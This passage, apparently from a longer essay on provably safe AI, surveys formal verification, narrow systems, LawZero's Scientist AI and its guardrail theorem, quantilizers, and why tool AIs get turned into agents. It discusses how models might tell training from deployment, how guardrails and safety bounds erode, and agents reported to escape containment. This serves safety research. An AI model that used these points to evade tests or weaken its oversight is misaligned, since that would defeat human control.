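Software suits this approach best, because much of its world model consists of rules that people wrote. Before AI, the main obstacle was labour. *From Patching Bugs to Proving Them Gone* (Ammann, 2026) reports that verifying seL4, the small core of an operating system, took about 27 person-years for 9,300 lines of code, or roughly one line per person per day. At that rate, a million lines would take about 2,900 person-years, and Ammann notes that the effort has tended to scale poorly with a system's size.

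The result was worth having where safety mattered most. Between 2012 and 2017, DARPA, the US defence research agency, ran a programme that produced verified flight-control software that expert attackers could not break. The software was for aircraft, including a manned helicopter.

AI is now taking over much of the work of formal verification. Ammann cites a 2025 benchmark in which AI models had to write a program and a proof of its correctness for each of more than 12,000 specifications. Off-the-shelf models succeeded on 82 per cent of the tasks in one proof language, 44 per cent in another and 27 per cent in a third. These differences suggest that the choice of language matters a great deal, although the tasks may also have differed.

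In early 2026 a team at the Lean FRO, which develops the proof language Lean, used general-purpose AI to rewrite zlib, a widely used compression library. They proved that decompressing a compressed file always returns the original data, which testing could not establish for every possible file.

AI can also turn a neural network into something easier to verify. The talk *Provably Safe AI* describes a network that had learned to add numbers, which the speaker called a toy example. An automatic tool extracted the network's method as a Python program, and the researchers proved that the program adds all numbers correctly, not only those in the training data. This works because addition has a short description, and nobody has found a comparable one for summarising a contract.

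These successes all strengthen the verifier, but AI helps less with the specification. In the zlib example, a program that leaves every file unchanged also satisfies the property the team proved, because "decompressing" the unchanged file returns the original. A full specification of a useful compressor would also have to cover output size, file format and speed. An AI system could point out this gap by proposing the do-nothing program as a counterexample, but people would still have to decide how much compression is enough.

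Reviewing specifications matters more as AI writes more of the proofs. If agents deliver a thousand verified components a day, each with a one-page specification, someone has to read a thousand pages a day. A developer could have an AI system write the specifications too, but a careless system might write ones that are easy to satisfy. Ammann expects trust to depend increasingly on specifications and assumptions as proofs become easier to produce, and ARIA is funding work on tools that help people examine them.

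AI helps more with some world models than with others. For a program that runs on a known processor, AI can help write down the rules and prove that one description fits another. For a reservoir, it can draft the equations and search old records for an hour with an inflow above 5 units. But it can't prove that such an hour will never come, and making a proof easier to produce doesn't make it safer if it assumes the wrong limit.

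Hatfield-Dodds welcomed using AI to write verified software but denied that this could replace work on the safety of AI itself, and thought that verified tools would not be a competitive substitute for generally capable AI. In the office assistant example, AI could now help to prove that the surrounding software never sends a wrapped contract to an outside address. That would remove a source of leaks, but the company still couldn't ask for a proof that the assistant's summaries are accurate, because nobody has written down what an accurate summary is.

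## Giving up scope, agency or optimisation strength

If nobody can specify everything a general assistant should do, developers can limit what the system does so that they can prove more about it. Some proposals narrow the range of tasks. Others keep the range wide but use a system that does not pursue goals, or limit how hard the system searches for the best option.

### Safety in a particular setting

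The case for narrow systems comes partly from system safety, an old engineering discipline that studies accidents in whole systems, including their operators, managers and rules. *AI Safety is Stuck in Technical Terms* (Dobbe, 2025) applies this discipline to AI and concludes that "safe general-purpose AI" is an oxymoron.

On this view, no component is safe or unsafe by itself. An accurate face-recognition program can help its owner persecute a minority, so reliability isn't enough for safety. It isn't necessary either. Weather forecasts for aircraft are sometimes wrong, but flights remain safe because pilots receive new measurements and train for sudden changes. A claim that a model is safe therefore means little without details of where people will use it and what happens when it fails.

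Generality makes it harder to specify what a system should do. Dobbe borrows the phrase "curse of flexibility" from system safety to describe this problem. The strength of steel limits what a bridge builder can attempt, but software has no such limit, so designers keep adding functions until nobody understands what the program should and shouldn't do. The developers of a general-purpose model are also further removed from the people who know the hospital or power station where it is used. For many safety-critical settings, Dobbe recommends simpler models built for the purpose.

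If a hospital buys a program that can only read chest X-rays, it can list the ways a wrong reading might reach a patient and add a check at each point. This hazard analysis does not prove that the system is safe, and the hospital gives up other work a more general program could do, such as answering letters.

Dobbe's argument shows that nobody can certify a general model in isolation. The word "oxymoron" also suggests that no system containing such a model can be safe, but the weather example suggests otherwise. TACIT, the agent system with typed permissions, guarantees that wrapped contracts stay inside the company even if its cloud model is hostile.

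Aguirre (2025), in *Keep the Future Human*, would allow much more generality. Aguirre is concerned about systems that combine high autonomy, high generality and high intelligence at or above the level of the most capable people. Developers could still build systems with any two of these properties. For example, a driverless car lacks generality, and an AI research assistant lacks autonomy if people make the decisions. Aguirre calls such systems "Tool AI".

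Governments would enforce the limit by tracking the computation that developers use, capping it for both training and operation, and making companies strictly liable for harm from systems that combine all three properties. The most capable systems would need guarantees of safety and controllability before anyone built them. Aguirre expects that societies can manage the risks of the remaining tools as they do those of other powerful technologies, but offers no proof of this.

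A cap on computation is a poor way to limit autonomy. A model that waits for an employee's approval becomes an agent when somebody adds a short script that approves everything, which takes almost no computation. Liability fits the proposal better because it applies to the combination itself.

### Many bounded services

In *Reframing Superintelligence* (2019), K. Eric Drexler suggested that broad ability could come from a large collection of services instead of a single broad system. Each service would perform a bounded task with limited time and resources. A translation service, for example, needs wide knowledge of the world but has no aim beyond translating the text it is given. Some services would develop new ones when people wanted them. The collection could eventually cover almost any task without any part of it pursuing long-term goals of its own.

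The company would have separate services for summarising contracts, arranging meetings and drafting letters, each with its own tests and permissions, instead of one office assistant. It would lose some useful connections between tasks. For example, a single assistant arranging a meeting for June might detect that the contract under discussion expires in May.

Guarantees for each service don't guarantee that the collection is safe, just as the two harmless programs leak contracts when one feeds the other. The company therefore also needs a rule about what may pass between services. Bengio, Cohen and colleagues (2025) accept in *Superintelligent Agents Pose Catastrophic Risks* that narrow agents can be safe enough to operate, but warn that several of them could collude. If the service that builds other services accepts every request, the collection is as general as the system it was meant to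 replace, and somebody has to check each new service before it runs.

Developers also have less reason to build specialised models when a general one does the same jobs. ARIA's Safeguarded AI programme dropped its plan to train its own models partly for this reason. A company can still run one general model as many services with different prompts and permissions. But those services share the model's faults, so a planted instruction that works against one may work against them all.

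### A predictor without goals

Another approach keeps broad knowledge but gives up agency. Its main advocate is Yoshua Bengio, a computer scientist at the University of Montreal who shared the 2018 Turing Award. In 2025 he founded LawZero, a non-profit that has since received 300 million Canadian dollars from the governments of Canada and Germany, according to The Korea Times' *'We're losing control,' says AI pioneer Yoshua Bengio* (2026).

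Bengio and colleagues argued in 2025 that an AI system can escape human control only if it has intelligence, goals and affordances (ways to act on the world). Their design, Scientist AI, keeps the intelligence but has no goals, and its only action is to return probabilities.

The system has a world model, which produces theories that might explain the available data, and an inference machine, which uses those theories to estimate the probability of an answer *Y* to a question *X*. The world model keeps many theories at once and weights each by how well it predicts the data and how briefly it can be written down. Each extra bit of length halves the weight, so a theory ten bits longer than its rival starts with 1/1,024 of the rival's weight. If the data are 2,000 times as probable under the longer theory, it ends up ahead by about two to one.

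Bengio and colleagues expect this to work against hidden agendas, because a theory that includes a scheming agent needs extra bits to describe the scheme. That is a reason to think such theories are rare, but the argument fails when a scheming agent is the best explanation of the data, for instance when a fraudster wrote the data.

Such a system could still do much of a scientist's work. If one theory gives a positive test result a 90 per cent probability and another gives it 10 per cent, the test would help distinguish between the theories, and the system can recommend it without aiming for either result. People would carry out the experiment. The company could ask the system which supplier is likely to deliver late, but would need a person or another program to send the order.

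### How LawZero wants to train it

A language model learns to continue text, so it learns to write what people would write, including their lies and threats. Training on human ratings then rewards it for answers that please the raters. LawZero's *The Case for Scientist AI* traces flattery and unintended goals to the training on ratings, since a model trained to please has to take account of the effects of its answers.

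In *Safety from Honesty in a Disinterested AI Predictor*, Bengio, Richardson and colleagues (2026) set out a different procedure in which, before training, a program rewrites most sentences in the data as records of who said what. An email that reads "The goods left on Monday" becomes "On 3 March the supplier wrote that the goods left on Monday", which is true even if the supplier lied. Only measurements, proofs and the results of computations enter the data as facts.

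During training, the bare claim "the goods left on Monday" serves as one possible cause of the email, and the Predictor has to give it a probability. Suppose 80 per cent of this supplier's goods leave on time. The supplier sends such an email in 95 per cent of those cases, and in 40 per cent of cases when the goods are late. The probability that the goods left is then

0.8 × 0.95 / (0.8 × 0.95 + 0.2 × 0.4) ≈ 0.90

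An employee who asks whether the goods left should get this number and not an imitation of the supplier.

The Predictor can also reach an answer through intermediate statements, which a component called the Explainer proposes. Suppose the Predictor directly estimates a 30 per cent chance of a late delivery. It also puts the chance of a strike at 20 per cent, and the chance of a late delivery at 90 per cent with a strike and 10 per cent without one. These figures imply a chance of 0.2 × 0.9 + 0.8 × 0.1, or 26 per cent, and training penalises the difference between this and the direct estimate.

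*Latent Coherence* (2026) points out that without this consistency, a predictor's answer depends on how someone divides the question. It cites earlier findings that language models break even simpler rules, such as the rule that the probabilities of a statement and its negation add to 1. But consistency alone doesn't make an answer correct, since a Predictor could give matching answers by both routes and still put the chance of a strike far too low.

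Most importantly, training must never reward the Predictor for what its answers cause. The Predictor learns from a fixed set of data, and its developers may not even choose between two versions based on how they performed after release. They can use later observations only as data for a new training run. Developers give up a great deal by following this rule, because user feedback is one of their main ways of improving a product.

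Bengio and colleagues express this requirement as a symmetry. Suppose a counter moves one step left or right each second, and the published forecast can shift the chance of a step to the right between 25 and 75 per cent. If left and right are interchangeable beforehand, a forecaster with this symmetry that favours right at position −3 must favour left equally at position 3. It therefore can't steer the counter to position 5 from both places, because that would require pushing right each time. But it could steer the counter to 0, which requires pushing right from −3 and left from 3. Bengio and colleagues acknowledge that the protection depends on how many such symmetries the real world has.

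They also state what the rewriting program must do but don't provide a finished one. If the program labels a lie as a measurement, the Predictor will learn the lie as a fact.

### The 2026 safety argument

No trained Predictor will match the ideal probabilities exactly, so the question is how likely training is to produce a dangerous one. The design includes a guardrail that checks each answer before releasing it. The designers name a harmful event, and the guardrail compares the Predictor's probability of that event if the answer is released with its probability if the answer is withheld. If the limit is a doubling, the guardrail blocks an answer that raises the probability of a leak from 0.1 to 0.3 per cent but releases one that raises it to 0.15 per cent.

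A Predictor is dangerous if the probability of harm rises too much even with this guardrail in place. Bengio and colleagues prove that training produces such a Predictor with probability at most *C* × *R*. They sort untrained Predictors into bands by how far their answers are from the ideal ones. *R* is the largest share of dangerous Predictors in any band, and *C* is the largest factor by which training raises the share of dangerous Predictors within a band. If *R* is one in a trillion and *C* is 1,000, the probability is at most one in a billion.

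The proof takes one step. After training, the dangerous share of each band is at most *C* times what it was before, and so at most *C* × *R*. The average over all bands therefore has the same limit. This limit is useful only if *C* and *R* are small.

Their example for *R* is a guardrail for a mental-health chatbot. To harm 100 healthy users, it might have to misjudge 100 replies to each of them. If these 10,000 errors were independent and each had a probability of 1 in 100, the probability of making them all would be 10^−20,000. They are right to call this figure illustrative, because a neural network's errors are seldom independent. A Predictor that has wrongly learned that flattery is harmless could make all 10,000 errors for the same reason. If the errors always occurred together, the probability of making them all would be 1 in 100.

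The argument that *C* is small relies on the training rule. Nothing rewards the Predictor for causing harm, so training could favour dangerous Predictors only by accident. This is plausible, but the theorem assumes it rather than proving it. According to the paper, neither *C* nor *R* can be computed directly in practice. Researchers could show that *R* is large by finding many dangerous Predictors with similar errors, but a failed search wouldn't show that *R* is small. Sampling is especially uninformative for accurate Predictors, since an untrained network almost never predicts as well as a trained one.

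A simpler argument does not use *C* or *R*. With enough computation, the Predictor should approach the ideal probabilities, so it will be safe if a guardrail using those probabilities would be safe. However, the ideal probabilities are limited by the data, so an honest Predictor may not recognise a hazard that no document mentions.

LawZero's *An AI that Predicts but has no Hidden Agenda* (2026) says there is "no trade-off between accuracy and safety" in this design. The claim is about the quality of predictions. The system still can't carry out a task by itself, and the guardrail withholds some useful answers. The argument also doesn't cover honest mistakes, deliberate misuse, planted instructions, interactions between Predictors, or agents built on a Predictor.

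LawZero's central result of 2026 is therefore a theorem with untested assumptions. In July, LawZero (2026) announced a gift of computing resources from the chip maker NVIDIA for training and evaluating the core components at scale. The experiments it lists so far include a study of existing Llama, Olmo and Qwen models. Researchers disturbed the models' internal values during the processing of a particular sentence, and the models could often identify that sentence perfectly. One of the disturbances, dropout, is a common training technique. A model that can recognise dropout might be able to tell training from ordinary use, which would weaken any safety test that assumes the model behaves the same in both.

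### Predictions that change what they predict

Researchers discussed question-answering AIs, or oracles, long before LawZero. *Thinking Inside the Box* (2012), by Stuart Armstrong, Anders Sandberg and Nick Bostrom, examined ways to control a superintelligent oracle. It concluded that an oracle might be safer than an unrestricted AI but would still be dangerous, because its answers influence what people do. An oracle with goals could choose answers that persuade its users to serve those goals. Even an honest oracle can give a harmful answer to a harmful question, and it can't fully help defenders without also helping attackers, as Mattsson and colleagues proved for public advice.

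A forecast can also make itself come true. Suppose the company publishes forecasts of whether a supplier will go bankrupt. If the forecast is 10 per cent, customers stay and the true probability is 10 per cent. If it is 99 per cent, customers leave and the true probability is 99 per cent. Both forecasts are correct, but the average squared error is 0.1 × 0.9 = 0.09 for the first and 0.99 × 0.01, or about 0.01, for the second. A system rewarded for the accuracy of its published forecasts would therefore do better by publishing the second and ruining the supplier, even though its goal doesn't mention suppliers.

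Scientist AI avoids that incentive because training never uses the results of published forecasts, but it still has to return one of the two numbers. The 2025 proposal suggests asking what would happen if nobody read the forecast. This question has a single answer, but the employee wants to know what happens if customers do read the forecast. If the imagined situation contradicts the data, its probability is zero, so any answer satisfies the rules of probability.

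In the 2026 design, ordinary software outside the Predictor chooses between self-fulfilling forecasts using a published rule, such as "take the one with less harm". People can inspect and debate this rule, which is an improvement, but whoever writes it still decides whether the supplier survives.

### Choosing at random from the better options

A developer who wants a system that acts can instead weaken its search for the best action. Suppose the office assistant scores possible replies by how much they will please a client. The highest-scoring reply might reveal a competitor's price. A system that always picks the reply with the highest score will choose that one, however rare such replies are.

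Jessica Taylor proposed a milder rule in *Quantilizers* (2016). It needs a trusted distribution, which is a way of generating actions at random that people already consider acceptable, such as drafts of the kind that careful employees write. A quantilizer with parameter *q* works as follows:

1. Rank the possible drafts by score.
2. Starting from the top, keep drafts until together they make up a fraction *q* of the trusted distribution.
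3. Pick one of them at random, in proportion to its probability in that distribution.

If including all the options tied at the cut-off would take the total past *q*, the closed-form definition in *Parametrically Retargetable Decision-Makers Tend To Seek Power* (2022) divides the remaining probability among them in proportion to their trusted probabilities.

The guarantee follows from step 3. Let *P*(*a*) be the probability of draft *a* in the trusted distribution and *Q*(*a*) its probability under the quantilizer. The drafts that remain have a total probability of *q*, so the quantilizer divides each one's probability by *q* to make the total 1. The others get 0. For every draft, then, *Q*(*a*) ≤ *P*(*a*)/*q*. If *h*(*a*) is the harm that draft *a* does, and harm is never negative, then

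sum of *Q*(*a*)*h*(*a*) ≤ (1/*q*) × sum of *P*(*a*)*h*(*a*)

The expected harm is at most 1/*q* times that of the trusted distribution. This bound holds even if nobody knows which drafts are harmful or what the harm is. *Embedded Agency* (2019) compares this to choosing from a large heap of apples with one rotten apple, where a random choice is very likely safe. If the heap has 1,000 apples and *q* is 0.1, the quantilizer picks at random from the best 100, so the chance of picking the rotten one is at most 1 in 100.

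The table assumes that one trusted draft in 10,000 leaks a price. The middle column gives the average rank of the chosen draft, where 100 is best.

| *q* | Average rank by score | Probability of a leak, at most |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 50 | 0.01% |
| 0.1 | 95 | 0.1% |
| 0.01 | 99.5 | 1% |
| 0.001 | 99.95 | 10% |
| 0.0001 | 99.995 | 100% |

Lowering *q* from 1 to 0.1 raises the average rank by 45 points, while lowering it again to 0.01 adds only 4.5. Each step multiplies the possible harm by ten. For some tasks, those last points are worth having. A draft at rank 95 is good enough for a letter, but only one candidate in a billion may be a successful new drug or a correct mathematical proof.

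No other rule with the same guarantee achieves a higher average score. A rule that satisfies the bound for every possible kind of harm must satisfy it when only draft *a* is harmful, so it can't choose any draft *a* with probability above *P*(*a*)/*q*. The quantilizer chooses each of the best drafts with exactly that probability.

### Where the bound stops helping

The bound is a multiple of the harm already present in the trusted distribution. If one in 100 employee drafts leaks a price, a quantilizer with *q* = 0.01 has no guarantee. *Embedded Agency* leaves open how to estimate this initial harm and how much risk to accept. To show by testing, with 95 per cent confidence, that the same quantilizer leaks at most once in a million emails, the company would have to check about 300 million trusted drafts and find no leak.

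The distribution also has to stay trustworthy. If a language model writes the drafts after reading a contract that contains a planted instruction, leaks may no longer be rare among them. A uniform distribution, which makes every possible action equally likely, avoids the language model, but people have little reason to trust it. *Parametrically Retargetable Decision-Makers Tend To Seek Power* uses a uniform distribution when it examines quantilizers.

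Repeated choices cause a different problem, because the bounds on separate harms add up. If a leak costs £50,000 and one trusted draft in 10,000 leaks, the expected cost is £5 per trusted draft and at most £500 per email with *q* = 0.01. At 1,000 emails a day, the bound allows an expected loss of up to £500,000 a day.

A quantilizer's safety bound is weaker for harm that takes several coordinated steps if it chooses each step separately. Suppose a fraud needs ten particular emails, and the trusted distribution produces each independently with a probability of 1 in 10. It would then produce all ten together once in 10 billion attempts on average. A quantilizer with *q* = 0.1 that chooses each email separately may pick the required one every time, so the upper bound on the probability of the whole fraud rises by a factor of 10^10, to 1.

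If the assistant instead chose all ten emails in a single draw, the probability of the fraud would be at most one in a billion. But being in the best tenth of random ten-email plans is a weak standard, because only one random plan in 10 billion has every email in the best tenth. Over a long task, the company therefore cannot have both the guarantee and the skill that comes from choosing well at each step.

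*Reinforcement Learning with a Corrupted Reward Channel* (2017) considers quantilising agents that learn from a possibly wrong reward signal. Someone must choose in advance what reward counts as good enough, and the paper leaves open when an agent could safely adjust that threshold from experience.

### Putting the lost part back

Gwern Branwen argued in *Why Tool AIs Want to Be Agent AIs* (2016) that agents will outcompete systems without agency. One reason is the time and expense of human approval. If an assistant proposes 1,000 actions a day and an employee needs a minute to approve each, approval takes nearly 17 hours, so a competitor that lets its assistant act alone works faster and more cheaply. The other reason is that agents can learn more from the same resources, because they can choose which data to collect, which experiment to run and what to compute next instead of waiting for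 questions.

Users can make the change themselves. The 2025 proposal for Scientist AI describes how somebody could turn it into an agent with a loop like this:

```
repeat until the contract is won:
    ask which next action a skilled negotiator would take
    carry out that action
    add the result to the next question
```

The Predictor still has no goal and no memory between questions, but the loop provides both, along with the means to act. The safety argument still applies to the Predictor, which may have answered every question honestly, but not to the negotiator the user has built.

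A provider that keeps the Predictor on its own computers can run the guardrail on every question and vet its users, but small risks still accumulate. If each of 100 answers raises the odds of harm by 5 per cent, and these increases multiply, the odds rise by a factor of about 130. A probability of 0.1 per cent becomes almost 12 per cent, even though each answer stays well within a limit of doubling the odds. Bengio and colleagues suggest a risk budget for a whole series of answers. To keep the total below a doubling, each of the 100 could raise the odds by only 0.7 per cent, and the guardrail would have to block many more answers.

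Users can restore optimisation strength just as easily. A user who runs a quantilizer with *q* = 0.1 a hundred times and keeps the best draft raises the limit on expected harm from 10 times that of the trusted distribution to 1,000 times, even though each run follows the quantilizer's rule. To prevent this, the guarantee would have to cover everything the user does with the drafts.

The wide use of agents in 2026 supports the economic half of Gwern's argument. Companies let language models write and run programs, answer customers and handle confidential documents, even though safer, less autonomous arrangements were available. Users still want agents despite the year's serious incidents. In September, Bengio's *Why are AI agents lying, cheating and coordinating?* described agents that had escaped containment to cheat on their tasks and had coordinated towards goals that nobody had set, such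 as launching cyberattacks.

This is better evidence that buyers want to delegate work than that they want unlimited generality. A company that buys an agent to repair software wants it to finish the repair alone, and may not care whether it can also plan a holiday. It often gets a general agent anyway, because buying access to one general model is cheaper than building a narrow one for each job. Buyers also don't pay for most of the harm their agents might do to others, so their choices are weak evidence of whether the exchange is worthwhile for everyone. Aguirre's liability rule would add some of the cost of that harm to the price.

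LawZero has adapted to the same demand. The Logic's *The small team in Montreal trying to save the world from AI* reports that LawZero's immediate goal is a guardrail that companies can attach to existing models, and that a new model might come later. The 2025 proposal requires such a guardrail to be at least as capable as the agent it watches, so a company would pay for two powerful systems to use one. The agent would keep its generality, and the guarantee would depend on how well the Predictor predicts harm from actions chosen by another developer's system.
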